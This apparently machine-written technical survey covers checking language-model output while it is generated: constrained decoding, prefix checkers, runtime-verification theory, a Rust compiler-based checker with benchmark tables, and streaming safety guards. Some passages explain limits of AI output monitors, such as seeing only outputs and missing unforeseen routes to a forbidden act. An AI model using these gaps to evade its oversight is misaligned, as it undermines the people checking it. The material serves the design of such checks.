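# Checking language model output while it is being generated

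## What can be known about an unfinished output

A language model writes its output in order, one small piece at a time, so a program that reads the pieces as they arrive can judge the text before it is finished. If the program finds a problem, it can stop the model or send it back to an earlier point. This can keep the model from writing four hundred more lines after a mistake on line 4. However, a fragment may not show whether the complete output will be acceptable. Half a function does not compile, even if the whole function would, and the second half of a paragraph may withdraw what the first half says. How much a check can establish about a fragment depends heavily on the rule it checks, and computer scientists worked out most of the theory behind this long before language models existed.

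### One token at a time

A language model generates text in tokens, which are words, parts of words or punctuation marks from a fixed vocabulary. *Generative Compilation* (Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues, 2026) describes the procedure. The model takes the prompt, *x*, followed by the text so far, *c*, called the prefix, and computes a probability for every token in the vocabulary. The system draws one token from that distribution, appends it to *c* and repeats until it draws a special token that marks the end. The loop never revises the prefix, so each token in it is part of the input for every later token, just as the prompt is.

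An early error therefore changes what the model conditions on at every later step. A crude way to estimate the damage is to assume that each step is right with probability *p*, independently of the others, and that the model never repairs an error. Then *t* steps all succeed with probability *p*^*t*. *The Illusion of Diminishing Returns* (Sinha, Arun and colleagues, 2025) uses this to show that a model stays above a success rate *s* for about ln(*s*)/ln(*p*) steps. At 99% accuracy per step, the chance of a flawless run falls below one half at step 69.

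Their experiments suggest that errors are not independent, and that a model is more likely to make a mistake when its history already contains some. They gave models a dictionary of words and integers, asked for a running sum over many turns, and then rewrote the history so that a chosen share of the earlier answers was wrong. Accuracy at turn 100 fell as that share rose, even in models with more than 200 billion parameters, which were nearly perfect at the same turn when the history had no errors. Qwen3 models that reason before they answer did not show the effect, possibly because the history left out their earlier reasoning. The task is synthetic, and the errors were in previous turns rather than in the same answer, so the result applies to a single long output only by analogy.

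*Beyond Exponential Decay* (2025) argues that a uniform error rate per token cannot explain why long outputs often hold together and why models routinely correct themselves midway. It proposes that errors concentrate at a few key tokens, while grammar and context almost determine the rest. Some evidence from code fits this proposal. In *Focused-DPO*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2025) sampled 20 programs for one problem from a coding model with 7 billion parameters. The programs shared their beginnings and endings and differed mainly at a few points in between. The model produced correct code up to 90.02% of the time when it continued from the right version of such a point, compared with 3.17% from the wrong version. These figures are an extreme and not an average, because the method selects points partly for how large this difference is.

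The chance of success can also drop suddenly during mathematical reasoning. *Inject a Turn, Not a Token* (2026) reports an experiment on failed attempts by Qwen3-4B, a small open model, at problems from the 2026 AIME, an American mathematics competition. The experimenters cut each attempt at ten evenly spaced places and sampled 16 continuations from every cut. In the attempts shown, continuations from early cuts often reached a correct answer, but at later cuts the success rate dropped sharply and stayed low.

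If errors were spread evenly through an output, a check would be about equally useful anywhere. If a few decisions determine the outcome, checks are much more useful soon after those decisions than elsewhere, but the decisions aren't marked in advance.

### Three moments for a check

A check can run before the system chooses a token, after a step, or after the whole output is complete. Checking before the system chooses a token is called constrained decoding. Software removes the tokens that would break a rule, and the system samples from the rest. A step is whatever unit the builder picks, such as a statement, a sentence or a proposed tool call (the model's request for outside software to perform an action). Checking the complete output is called post-generation checking, and it is how most people use a compiler today.

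Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues compare the three on an eight-line function in Rust, a language whose compiler rejects programs that could misuse memory. The function borrows part of a message under the name `tag` on line 2, changes the message on line 3, and uses `tag` on line 4, which Rust forbids after such a change. A post-generation check reports the error only after line 8. In a longer file, the later code would build on the mistake, and the model would receive many diagnostics (the explanations that come with a fail verdict) at once.

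Constrained decoding blocks the error at its first forbidden token, the full stop after `tag` on line 4. But the sensible repair is on line 2, which constrained decoding cannot change, and the model isn't told why the token was blocked. It can only continue by extending `tag` into a longer name that the program has yet to define, which few programmers would write. Constrained decoding also requires access to the model's token probabilities and sampling, which companies that sell frontier models through an API generally do not provide.

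A check after the step also catches the error on line 4, and it can return an explanation so that the model goes back and rewrites line 2. The checker needs something complete enough to judge. Compilers can process unfinished code once other software has closed its open structures. In *Verifiers in the Loop*, Zhou, Christodorescu and colleagues (2026) run checks at the ends of statements, blocks, functions and whole programs, and let a check return "not applicable" when it doesn't suit the fragment.

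### The prefix checker and its two errors

Let *L* be the set of acceptable complete outputs: all Rust programs that compile, say, or all letters without a false claim. A prefix checker *P* takes a prefix *c* and should accept it exactly when some continuation *w* would make the whole acceptable:

*P*(*c*) = true if and only if there is a *w* such that *c* followed by *w* is in *L*.

A prefix with no such *w* is a dead end. A checker makes a false rejection if it rejects *c* although a suitable *w* exists, and a miss if it accepts *c* although none exists. A checker that never makes a false rejection is "complete", and one that never makes a miss is "sound". A checker can be complete by accepting everything or sound by rejecting everything, but it is hard to be both. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues point out that exact prefix checking is undecidable in general for expressive rules about what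 code means, so no algorithm gets every prefix right.

The two technical names can mislead because usage varies. *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies* (2026), which is about monitors for groups of AI agents, uses the phrase "sound one-sided alarm". This seems to mean an alarm that never goes off without cause, which is completeness in the sense above. The terms "false rejection" and "miss" avoid this ambiguity.

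Whether a check should risk missing errors or rejecting good output depends largely on when it runs. Constrained decoding cannot take a token back, so one missed error can leave it with no valid way to continue. If the system can return to an earlier point, a miss does less harm because a later check may still catch the error, while a false rejection discards good work and gives the model misleading feedback. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues therefore aim for no false rejections and accept some misses. Their reasoning holds for text that nobody has used yet, but not for a tool call that deletes a file, because a later check cannot undo the deletion.

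The definition also requires only that a valid continuation exist, however unlikely the model is to produce it. The odd path left open in the Rust function therefore counts. *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding* (2025) gives a more extreme example from a test with a 32-billion-parameter coding model, in which every failure of the constrained decoder was a generation that never ended. In one failure, the model was about to open a comment with two slashes, but the parser read the first slash as a division sign. The output then continued as endless junk, although a valid ending remained possible in principle throughout.

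In prose, whether a prefix is a dead end depends mostly on the choice of *L*. A letter that gives a wrong date can still be made acceptable if the rule is that no error may stand uncorrected, because the next sentence can fix it, but not if the rule is that no sentence may be false. *Limits of Reliability and Scaling in Language Models* (2026) makes a related distinction with a quantity called drift, the distance between the generated prefix and a reference prefix. If the distance measures meaning, a paraphrase has zero drift, and drift becomes positive only once the text's meaning puts the target out of reach.

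### Safety, liveness and the verdict "unknown"

Runtime verification, the field that checks running programs against formal rules, faced the same problem earlier. A monitor has to check a rule about a whole execution when only the beginning is available. In *Runtime Verification for LTL and TLTL*, Bauer, Leucker and Schallhart (2007) argue that two verdicts are too few and use three: *false* if no continuation satisfies the rule, *true* if every continuation does, and *inconclusive* otherwise. Their running example is the rule that no thread may start before the program has initialised. The rule is permanently broken if a thread starts first and permanently satisfied if initialisation comes first. Until one of these happens, the verdict is inconclusive.

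A prefix checker that can only accept or reject combines the second and third verdicts. It accepts both a prefix that already guarantees success and one that might still go wrong on the next line, so acceptance does not mean that the finished output will succeed. Zhou and colleagues use "not applicable" for a different case, in which the check has not run at all.

A safety property is a rule whose violations always show in some finite prefix, after which no continuation can repair them. The standard form is "always *p*". The rule need not concern harm; "every bracket closes the most recent open one" is also a safety property. A liveness property is a rule that no finite prefix can violate, because some continuation could still satisfy it. *Runtime Verification for LTL in Stochastic Systems* (2025) gives a stronger, informal definition: no finite prefix reveals whether the property holds.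 That definition fits "*p* happens again and again without end", but it does not quite fit "eventually *q*", which becomes true as soon as *q* happens. Bauer and colleagues class "eventually *q*" as co-safety, the counterpart of safety, because a prefix can confirm it but never refute it.

Take a Python function that the model has not finished:

```python
def save_report(rows):
    f = open("/tmp/report.csv", "w")
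    for row in rows:
        f.write(row)
```

Suppose a monitor follows the file operations in order, as though each line ran as soon as the model wrote it. The property "never writes outside /tmp" has held so far, but the next line could violate it. If that line opens `/home/ana/notes.txt` in mode `"w"`, Python empties the file at once, and nothing the model writes afterwards can undo the violation. The property "eventually closes the file" cannot be violated while the output is unfinished, because the next line could always contain a call to `f.close()`.

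| What happens next | "Never writes outside /tmp" | "Eventually closes the file" |
|---|---|---|
| Another write to the same file | unknown | unknown |
| A write to /home/ana | fail | unknown |
| A call to `f.close()` | unknown | pass |
| The output ends here | pass | fail |

The last row departs from the classical theory, which deals with executions that go on forever. A model's output ends, and at that point each of the two rules has been either satisfied or broken. A final check is still needed after checking during generation, because violations of some rules can only be detected once the output is complete.

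Adding a deadline partly solves this problem. "Closes the file within ten statements" is a safety property, because the rule is already broken if the file is still open after the tenth statement. *SoK* (2026), a survey of formal methods for fact-checking, gives "a drift alarm fires within k steps" as a rule that a monitor can check on a system built around a language model. But the limit of ten is arbitrary, and a correct function that closes its file on the twelfth statement now fails.

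Bauer and colleagues call a rule monitorable if every prefix has some finite continuation that would settle whether the rule is satisfied or violated. They show that some monitorable rules are neither safety nor co-safety rules. *Runtime Verification* (2026), a set of lecture notes, proves that negating a monitorable rule, or joining two with "and", gives another monitorable rule. A builder can therefore combine short monitorable rules in these ways into a long policy that is still monitorable.

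All of this assumes that someone can tell, at each step, whether *p* is true. This is usually possible for a file write, but it is the main difficulty for prose. TemporalGuard, a system that *SoK* describes, treats a conversation with a model as an execution and translates each message into elementary true-or-false statements before it applies any rule. It then applies the rules exactly, but its verdict can be no more reliable than the translation. *Watchdogs and Oracles* (2025) notes that a monitor can generally access only the outputs and a few internal signals, such as token probabilities, and not the rest of the model's reasoning state.

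### What stopping a program can enforce

Detecting a violation is different from preventing it. In *Enforceable Security Policies*, Schneider (2000) asked which policies can be enforced by a mechanism that only watches a program's steps and terminates the program when the next step would break the policy. He derived his answer from what such a mechanism lacks.

A mechanism that monitors a running program observes only one execution, so the policy it enforces must be a rule about single executions. This excludes information flow policies, because whether a secret leaks into a value depends on what that value would have been in other runs. The mechanism also cannot observe the future. It must reject a prefix that is unacceptable as it stands, even if some continuation would make the execution acceptable, because the program might halt there. Finally, every rejection must come after finitely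 many steps. Policies that meet all three conditions are safety properties, so such a mechanism can enforce only safety properties.

A monitor with two states can enforce the rule "Send no message after reading a file." It moves to the second state at the first file read and blocks all sending from then on. A monitor cannot enforce "A customer who pays receives the service," because it can stop a seller from doing anything other than serving a customer who has paid, but it cannot make the seller serve.

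The second condition is stricter than anything a prefix checker requires. A prefix checker accepts a fragment that is unacceptable now if some continuation could still make it acceptable, but Schneider's monitor has to reject that fragment. The lenient rule is right for unreleased text, because the system can discard the text without effect if generation stops. A running program needs the strict rule because the steps it has carried out can't be discarded, so each one must leave things in a state that would be tolerable if nothing further happened. The strict rule therefore applies once a builder starts running unfinished code instead of only reading it.

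Even some safety properties cannot be enforced by terminating a program. "Nobody waits for the resource longer than a set number of seconds" is a safety property, but time keeps passing after the program stops. If the limit is set in execution steps instead, termination does enforce it. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues, 2012) builds this into the theory by separating actions that a mechanism can prevent from actions that it can only observe. A mechanism checking a language model can still block a sentence held in a buffer, but it can only observe one that is already on the user's screen. Holding back the whole output therefore allows more properties to be enforced. A system that releases no code until the file is closed enforces "eventually closes the file" on everything it releases, although the user has to wait.

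Schneider attaches two practical conditions, both relevant to generated code. The target must not be able to alter the monitor's state, or it can subvert the monitor. The monitor must also recognise every way of performing the forbidden act. A rule against sending messages can be evaded if the program has a way to send them that the rule's author did not know about. In the Python example, a monitor that looks only for calls to `open` would miss a shell command that writes to the home directory.

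These conditions put a builder's decisions in a rough order. The builder first chooses the check, because the rule determines whether an unfinished output can fail it. The next step is to set up isolation before any generated code runs. Both the check and the generation then need limits, because a verdict can stay unknown indefinitely and a model can keep writing without finishing. Finally, the builder decides whether to stop after a rejection or roll back, and how far. Rolling back means discarding the end of the prefix and generating again from an earlier saved state. The verdict alone is not enough to make this decision. In the Rust function, the compiler reported an error on line 4, but the line that needed changing was line 2.

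## Checking unfinished code without running it

A static check examines the text of a program without executing it. Static checks for unfinished code differ mainly in how many of a language's rules they cover. The simplest check only the grammar, which determines where brackets, commas and keywords may appear. Others also track which names exist at a given point, or which types of value fit there. Generative compilation covers the most rules, because it completes the fragment with placeholders and passes the result to the language's ordinary compiler.

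### Grammar masks

A parser is a program that reads code from left to right and keeps track of its structure. Its state after a prefix, the code read so far, determines which characters can come next. For example, in a tiny language, a value might be either a whole number or a comma-separated list of values in square brackets. After the prefix `[[4`, the parser's state consists of two open lists and an unfinished number, so the next character can be another digit, a comma or a closing bracket.

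A token can contain several characters, so the software feeds each candidate token to the parser one character at a time. It keeps the token only if the parser can accept all of them:

| Candidate token | Allowed | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `7` | yes | It extends the number. |
| `]` | yes | It closes the inner list. |
| `]]` | yes | It closes both lists. |
| `]]]` | no | The third bracket has nothing to close. |
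| `,[` | yes | It starts a new list inside the inner one. |
| `,]` | no | A value must follow the comma. |
| end marker | no | Two lists are still open. |

Checking every token in the vocabulary this way produces a mask, which marks each token as allowed or forbidden. The system sets the probability of every forbidden token to zero, rescales the others to add up to one, and samples. The rescaling also changes how likely the model is to produce each complete output. If the system samples `]]`, no list remains open, and the next mask allows only the end marker.

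Checking every token in the vocabulary at every step, which is called computing a full mask, can be slow. In *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, Mündler, He and colleagues (2025) sample a token first and check only that one. If it fails, they set its probability to zero and sample again from the same distribution, without running the model again. With Gemma 2 2B, a small open model, the first sample passed 99.4% of the time. When they computed full masks with the same checker, every test problem exceeded the five-minute limit. Each call to their checker is slow because it covers types as well as grammar. Earlier systems that covered only grammar did compute full masks.

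A grammar mask guarantees well-formed output, provided that the model finishes. For code, this guarantee is worth less than it might seem. In TypeScript programs from six open-weight models, Mündler and colleagues found that only 6% of compilation errors were errors of syntax. They give this unfinished function as an example:

```typescript
function is_int(text: string): boolean {
  const num = Number(text);
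  return !isNaN(num) && parseInt(num
```

In the unfinished code `parseInt(num`, the function `parseInt` takes text, but `num` is a number. A grammar mask blocks a semicolon here because a bracket is still open. It allows `ber`, which would produce the undeclared name `number`, and `()`, which would call a number as though it were a function. It also allows `, 10)`, which passes the number to `parseInt` unchanged. CodeLlama 34B, an open coding model, wrote `, 10)`, and the program did not compile. The continuation `.toString()`, which converts the number to text, would have been correct.

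### Looking up the valid names

In Java, the text after `server.` must name a field or method that belongs to the type of `server`. If that type is defined in a file that the prompt doesn't include, the model tends to invent a plausible name. Code editors have long solved this problem for human programmers with a language server, a program that reads the whole project, works out which names are valid and suggests them.

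*Monitor-Guided Decoding of Code LMs with Static Analysis of Repository Context* (Agrawal, Kanade and colleagues, 2023) connected such an analyser to the sampling loop. When the prefix ends with an object and a dot, a monitor queries the analyser for valid names and turns them into a mask. Suppose the valid names are `getName`, `getPort` and `close`. The mask allows tokens that begin one of these names, such as `get`, and tokens that complete a name and then end it, such as `close(`. If the model generates `get`, the monitor drops `close` from its list and shortens the other two entries to `Name` and `Port`. Once a name is complete, the monitor does nothing until the next object and dot. If the analyser finds no valid name, the system abandons the attempt.

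They tested this on 10,538 unfinished methods, made by cutting 1,420 methods from 100 Java projects at dots. With six samples per task, the monitor raised the estimated chance that at least one compiled from 60.0% to 73.0% for SantaCoder, a model with 1.1 billion parameters, and from 62.7% to 74.3% for text-davinci-003, an OpenAI model with 175 billion. SantaCoder with the monitor was thus more likely to produce code that compiled than text-davinci-003 without it, although the larger model's code still matched the original programmers' code more closely. These models are several generations old, so the percentages are a poor guide to current ones. The monitor helped less when the model already had more context, a pattern that is probably more durable. When SantaCoder also received the code after the gap and the relevant type definitions, the monitor raised the rate from 71.0% to 80.3%.

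The same design works with other triggers. In a test with only ten examples, Agrawal and colleagues used monitors to enforce the number of arguments in a call and, where a library requires it, the order of calls, such as not reading from a file after closing it. But each trigger covers one kind of mistake and the monitor doesn't check for others, so it often misses errors. Monitors also reject some correct code, because analysers rely on heuristics when code is incomplete. Agrawal and colleagues acknowledge that these heuristics can suggest wrong names and leave out correct ones, which the mask then prevents the model from writing.

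### Checking types at every character

Mündler and colleagues check types throughout the output, not only at selected points. An ordinary type checker determines whether a finished expression has the required type, but an unfinished expression can have the wrong type and still be completed correctly. In the `parseInt` example, `num` has the wrong type, but `num.toString()` has the right one. Their checker therefore has to determine whether any continuation would produce the required type.

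It does this by searching a graph in which each node is a type and each edge is an operation that leads from one type to another. From "number", the member `.toString` leads to "function that takes nothing and returns a string", and calling that function leads to "string". Because a path to "string" exists, the decoder accepts the prefix and allows only next characters that leave at least one such path available. It blocks `, 10)` because `num` would still be a number.

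The search might never end, because some operations produce ever more complicated types. Mündler and colleagues limit it with a rule of thumb that skips most types more complex than the starting type and the target. As a result, the checker sometimes rejects code that could still have become valid. By design, it never accepts code that can't be completed validly, because every path it finds corresponds to code that type-checks, and this makes it suitable for constrained decoding.

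The checker also records which variables exist and whether every path through a function returns a value. In one test, DeepSeek Coder 33B wrote a loop to find a number's largest divisor and then tried to end the function, although the loop could finish without returning anything. The decoder blocked the closing brace, and the model then added `return 1;`, which was correct.

All this required a second implementation of TypeScript's type rules, because the official compiler only checks complete programs. The new implementation covers part of the language and has 11,249 lines of Python and about 400 unit tests, while the official compiler has more than 427,000 lines. The new implementation also enforces some rules that TypeScript doesn't have, such as requiring a written type for every function parameter.

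Mündler and colleagues tested it on short programming problems from two standard collections, HumanEval and MBPP, with six open-weight models of 2 to 34 billion parameters. When the models wrote functions from a description, type constraints removed on average 75.3% of the compilation errors on HumanEval and 52.1% on MBPP. A perfect syntax check would have removed 9.0% and 4.9%. The share of programs that passed their tests rose by only 3.5% in relative terms, because most programs had compiled anyway and a program that compiles can still give wrong results. When the task was to repair a program that didn't compile, the relative gain was 37.0%.

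The experiment's design favors the method. Because the checker doesn't support all of TypeScript, the experimenters kept every program that compiled without constraints and regenerated only the failed ones under constraints. The results therefore leave out any cases where the checker would have wrongly blocked programs that had compiled. The figures are closer to what a checker for the full language might achieve than to what this one would achieve if it ran on every output.

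Many of the remaining errors came from generations that never finished. In one case, CodeLlama 34B tried to call `.sort` on a number. The decoder steered it to `.toString` instead, and the model kept adding text operations until it ran out of time. The checks also increased the median time per problem by 39.1% on HumanEval and 52.1% on MBPP, though Mündler and colleagues did not try to optimise the Python code.

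### Completing the program for the real compiler

Writing a second type checker for Rust would be a much larger project. The relevant part of the Rust compiler has about 600,000 lines, and its rules about which code may use a piece of memory, and for how long, can involve distant parts of a program. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues therefore use the existing compiler and change the program they give it. Their component, called a sealor, turns a prefix *c* into a complete program *S*(*c*). They accept *c* if *S*(*c*) compiles and reject it otherwise. The sealor should guarantee that *S*(*c*) compiles if any continuation of *c* does, which rules out false rejections.

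The function with `tag`, slightly simplified here, shows how this works. The model has just written the full stop on line 4:

```rust
fn label(msg: &mut String) -> String {
    let tag = &msg[..4];
    msg.drain(..4);
    let urgent = tag.
```

On line 3, `drain` deletes the part of `msg` that `tag` refers to, which requires exclusive access to `msg`. Rust forbids any use of `tag` after that, but the full stop means that the program will use `tag` however it is completed.

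The compiler can't process this fragment as it stands, so the sealor turns it into the following program:

```rust
fn label(msg: &mut String) -> String {
    let tag = &msg[..4];
    msg.drain(..4);
    &tag;
    hole_val()
}
```

Three rules produce the change. The rule for unfinished declarations drops `let urgent =` and keeps the expression on the right, which can already contain an error. The rule for unfinished member accesses drops the dot and keeps a reference to `tag`, since the model might have been about to call a method that only reads it. The rule for unfinished blocks adds a placeholder for the missing return value and a closing brace. The new program still uses `tag` after `drain`, so the compiler reports the same conflict it would have reported for the finished function. The model receives this report and makes `tag` an independent copy of the text on line 2.

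### Two placeholders

`hole_val()` represents a value that the model has yet to write. It calls a helper function whose declaration lets it return any type, so it fits wherever the program needs a value. The helper would crash if it ran, but it never runs. The compiler uses only the declaration, so it treats the program as continuing normally after the call and checks the code that follows.

The other placeholder, `hole_div()`, has the opposite purpose. It is Rust's `panic!()`, which stops the program, and the compiler knows that nothing after it can run. This matters for loops and branches. Suppose the model is in the middle of this loop:

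```rust
while more() {
    send(buffer);
```

If `send` takes ownership of `buffer`, the variable is empty afterwards, and a second pass through the loop would be an error unless the next line refills it. If the sealor only closed the brace, the compiler would report that error even though the model might still refill `buffer`. The sealor therefore adds `hole_div()` before the brace, so the loop can never reach a second pass and the compiler checks only the first. The sealor also fills a missing `else` branch with `hole_div()`, so that the missing branch doesn't constrain the finished one.

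Missing values need a separate placeholder, `hole_val()`, because Rust may give `panic!()` the type `()` if nothing else in the program determines its type. The compiler would then report type errors caused only by the sealing.

When the model has written only some of a function call's arguments, the sealor queries the compiler for the function's definition to determine how many are missing, then fills their places with `hole_val()`. If the model has already written too many arguments, the sealor leaves them in place and the compiler correctly rejects the call, since no continuation can remove the extra ones.

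### Errors that later code could cure

Some errors in a sealed program are real only if the model stops writing at that point. A function may call another function that appears further down the file. A type may still lack a method that it is declared to have, and a variable's type may be unclear until the program uses the variable. The checker suppresses such errors only where later code could still resolve them. For example, it ignores "missing method" errors only inside the definition that the model is currently writing. When the model finishes the file, the checker stops suppressing errors and the compiler reports them all.

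The remaining diagnostics refer to the sealed program, which the model never receives. The software therefore keeps a map of the text it copied unchanged from the prefix and uses it to attach each diagnostic to the corresponding place in the model's own code. It discards diagnostics that concern only inserted text. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues guarantee only the verdict, and have not proved that every diagnostic describes a real defect in the prefix.

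Even for the verdict, the strength of the guarantee depends on the language. For Featherweight Rust, a small formal model of Rust's memory rules, a proof checked with the proof assistant Lean shows that the sealor causes no false rejections. Another proof shows that it causes no misses at the end of a statement, because the sealed program is then one possible continuation of the prefix, so if it compiles, a valid continuation exists. For Rust itself, the argument is informal and covers one construct at a time. When the sealor has no rule for an unfinished construct, it deletes that construct and waits until the model has completed it. This causes no false rejections, but it delays detection.

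### Checking while the model continues

The model keeps writing while the compiler checks a prefix, and the software stores only the newest version of the text. When the compiler finishes, it checks that version next and skips those in between. A rejection therefore comes slightly late, and the system discards the few tokens the model wrote in the meantime. The method needs only a stream of text from the model, which commercial APIs provide.

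After a rejection, the system stops the model, adds the partial file and the diagnostic to the conversation, and has the model write the file again from the beginning. The model can copy the good part from its rejected attempt, but it has to generate that text again.

### Results on two Rust tasks

Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues tested seven models on two tasks in which compilation errors are frequent. The first was translation from C to Rust. They took the 100 translations in CRUST-Bench and removed the roughly 80 that two strong models could solve without feedback, which left 20. The second task, which they call UpdatedAPI, consisted of 30 small programs that depend on recently changed libraries, so the models' knowledge of those libraries was likely to be out of date. Each model attempted every problem twice.

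The experiments compared generation without feedback, ordinary compiler feedback after each complete file, and early feedback from the sealor. Both feedback methods allowed up to 20 retries for translation and 15 for the library task. Early feedback could use at most 10 of these retries for restarts in the middle of a file before switching to ordinary feedback.

Without feedback, 65.9% of the outputs failed to compile on average. Feedback after generation reduced this to 20.7%, and early feedback reduced it to 13.1%. Each cell in the table gives the result with feedback after generation, then the result with early feedback, in per cent.

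| Model | Translation: does not compile | Translation: passes tests | UpdatedAPI: does not compile | UpdatedAPI: passes tests |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 7.5 → 2.6 | 61.0 → 62.3 | 6.7 → 0.0 | 85.0 → 86.7 |
| GPT 5.3 Codex | 3.9 → 1.8 | 61.0 → 61.8 | 13.3 → 3.3 | 75.0 → 80.0 |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash | 14.0 → 10.5 | 50.4 → 52.2 | 16.7 → 13.3 | 78.3 → 80.0 |
| Kimi K2.7 Code | 38.6 → 11.0 | 39.9 → 53.9 | 13.3 → 3.3 | 76.7 → 83.3 |
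| GLM 5.2 | 17.1 → 15.4 | 51.3 → 50.4 | 45.0 → 16.7 | 53.3 → 71.7 |
| Qwen 3.5 397B | 13.2 → 12.7 | 54.8 → 53.1 | 21.7 → 15.0 | 68.3 → 71.7 |
| Qwen 3.5 9B | 36.0 → 35.1 | 30.3 → 33.3 | 43.3 → 43.3 | 48.3 → 41.7 |

Early feedback lowered the share of outputs that failed to compile in 13 of the 14 comparisons, nine of them by a statistically significant amount, and tied in the other. It had a smaller effect on whether the code worked. The share of outputs that passed their tests averaged 26.4% without feedback, 59.5% with feedback after generation and 63.0% with early feedback, so most of the improvement came from using a compiler at all. Two cases, Kimi on translation and GLM on the library task, account for about two thirds of the 3.5-point gain from early feedback. In the other twelve, the average gain was a little over one percentage point.

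In three cases, fewer programs passed their tests with early feedback. GLM 5.2 and the large Qwen model lost one or two points on translation. The smallest model, Qwen 9B, lost 6.6 points on the library task, and its programs compiled no more often. That loss is four of 60 programs and was not statistically significant, but wasted restarts could plausibly explain it. Qwen 9B used all ten early restarts in 40.9% of tasks, compared with 2.1% for GPT 5.3 Codex, and weaker models often wrote the same faulty beginning again. On the library task, a model that uses up its early restarts this way has only five retries left for ordinary feedback.

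The number of retries matters for stronger models too. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues pooled all models and counted compilable outputs after each retry. Ordinary feedback led at first because each of its reports covers every error in the file. Early feedback overtook it at the fourth retry and led by 4.4 percentage points at the seventh. They compared the methods by retries rather than tokens, although an early restart discards only part of a file.

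To measure how soon the checker finds an error, they took 961 faulty files from the runs without feedback and replayed them at 50 tokens per second. The checker reported an error a median of 3 lines after the place that the compiler names for the finished file, compared with 89 lines for a check at the end of the file. The checker's average delay was 27.7 lines, mainly because of the suppressed errors. A misspelled function name, for example, might refer to a function that the model has yet to write, so the checker usually can't report it until the file ends. Of the slowest quarter of detections, 90.5% involved missing names, imports, methods or functions.

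On average, the checker stopped a file after 33.3% of its length. It would have stopped at 32.7% if compilation had taken no time, so compiling while the model kept writing caused little delay. A simpler variant that checked only completed functions stopped files at 40.3% on average, with a median delay of 14 lines. A checker can therefore achieve much of the saving without a full set of rules for unfinished statements.

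Early reports are also shorter, which makes the original mistake easier to find. They contained 5.5 diagnostics on average, compared with 13.8 for reports on complete files. On the translation task, some reports on complete files contained several hundred.

Early feedback added an average of 135 seconds per task, compared with 233 for feedback after generation. The saving was largest for models that needed many retries. On translation, the average for Qwen 9B fell from 879 to 357 seconds. The time barely changed for Claude Opus 4.8, which made fewer mistakes. The compiler ran on a server with 192 processor cores, so a smaller machine might give a less favourable result.

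### Why this checker cannot control the sampling

The sealor would not work as a mask that blocks each token the compiler would reject, because it can miss errors. When the model has written `tag.` and part of a name, the sealor ignores the partial name and checks only `tag`. It would therefore accept `tag.zq`, although no method begins with those letters. Generative compilation recovers from this at a later check, but a constrained decoder could only add more letters to a name that will never be valid.

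The type-constrained decoder has the opposite weakness. It rejects a token whenever its search finds no valid continuation, even if one exists. A decoder can then pick another token, but a system that restarts after every rejection would throw away a good file. Moving a checker from one kind of system to the other therefore changes which mistakes it makes.

### Choosing a static check

| Method | Access to the model | What the builder has to write | What it covers |
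|---|---|---|---|
| Grammar mask | token probabilities | a grammar and a parser for prefixes | syntax |
| Monitor-guided decoding | token probabilities | a link to a language server and one trigger per rule | selected rules, mainly valid names |
| Type-constrained decoding | token probabilities | a second type checker | types, in part of TypeScript |
| Generative compilation | streamed text | a sealor and small changes to the compiler | the Rust compiler's rules, some only at the end of the file |
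| Compiling the finished file | finished text | almost nothing | all of the compiler's rules, at the end of the file |

Builders often can't use masks, because most models behind a commercial API don't give them the access that masks require. Output in JSON, a common data format, is an exception. Mündler and colleagues note that providers have built JSON constraints into their own services, so a builder who needs well-formed tool calls may not have to write any. Completing the unfinished code so that a real compiler can check it doesn't always avoid the restriction. Zhou and colleagues take this approach, but they use open-weight models because their system has to control the decoding directly.

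The sealor for Rust took about 5,000 lines of code, plus another 3,000 to connect it to the models. The sealor alone is less than half the size of Mündler and colleagues' type checker for part of TypeScript, and it covers a stricter language more fully. But it works only for Rust, and each new language needs its own rules for completing fragments. Monitor-guided decoding is the easiest to extend to other languages, since most already have a language server, but it checks the least beyond syntax.

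For a language without a sealor, checking each function as soon as the model completes it is a reasonable start, since that variant did well in Rust. It needs no placeholders inside the function, but the software still has to ignore references to code that comes later. Compiling the finished file is probably better for files of a few dozen lines, or when only two or three retries are allowed, because an early check can save little in those cases and a full report gives the model every error at once.

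## Judging unfinished prose and code with a trained classifier

Some properties, such as whether a letter threatens its reader or whether a program solves the problem the user described, can't be tested with a ready-made checker like a compiler. For these, a builder can train a classifier on labelled examples and use it to score each prefix. The score usually runs from 0 to 1 and estimates how likely the text is to be unacceptable. The system rejects the prefix when the score passes a threshold. A lower threshold catches more bad text but also stops more good text.

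Such a classifier estimates whether unfinished text is already harmful or will probably become harmful, which makes a high score evidence but not proof. It doesn't look for dead ends, which are rare in prose if a later sentence may correct an earlier one.

### A separate guard or a classifier inside the model

A streaming guard is a classifier that checks a model's answer for harmful content while the model is still writing it. The guard can be a separate language model that reads the user's request and the answer so far. Qwen3Guard-Stream, a family of guards with 0.6 to 8 billion parameters, works this way and gives a verdict after every token. A separate guard works with any model that streams its text, including models behind a commercial API, but the operator has to run a second model. *PGuard* (Alibaba AAIG, 2026) estimates that adding a large guard can raise the cost of serving a model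 to 2.7 times the original.

The alternative is a small classifier attached to the generating model. To compute the next token, a model produces long lists of numbers called activations, which encode what it has read and written so far. A classifier that takes these as input doesn't have to process the text again. *Kelp* (Li, Wu and colleagues, 2025) describes a classifier with 20 million parameters that keeps a compact memory of earlier tokens, updated at each new token. Generating 1,024 tokens took 23.10 seconds with the classifier and 22.68 seconds without it, a difference of 0.42 milliseconds per token. PGuard has a similar design and reduced the output speed of a model with 122 billion parameters by at most 2.3%.

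Only someone running the model can access its activations, and each model needs its own classifier. How well the classifier works also depends on which model wrote its training text. Li and colleagues found that a classifier for Qwen3-8B worked nearly as well when trained on answers from the related Qwen3-14B as on Qwen3-8B's own answers, but notably worse when trained on answers from Llama-3.1-8B.

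*NExT-Guard* (Fang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) combines the two designs. It runs a separate guard that normally classifies finished answers, but reads the guard's activations at every token instead of waiting for its final classification.

### Training with labels for whole responses

Most safety datasets label a response as harmful or harmless without marking where the harm begins. Training a classifier on the last token of each response is the obvious way to use these labels, but it teaches the classifier to be accurate only on complete responses.

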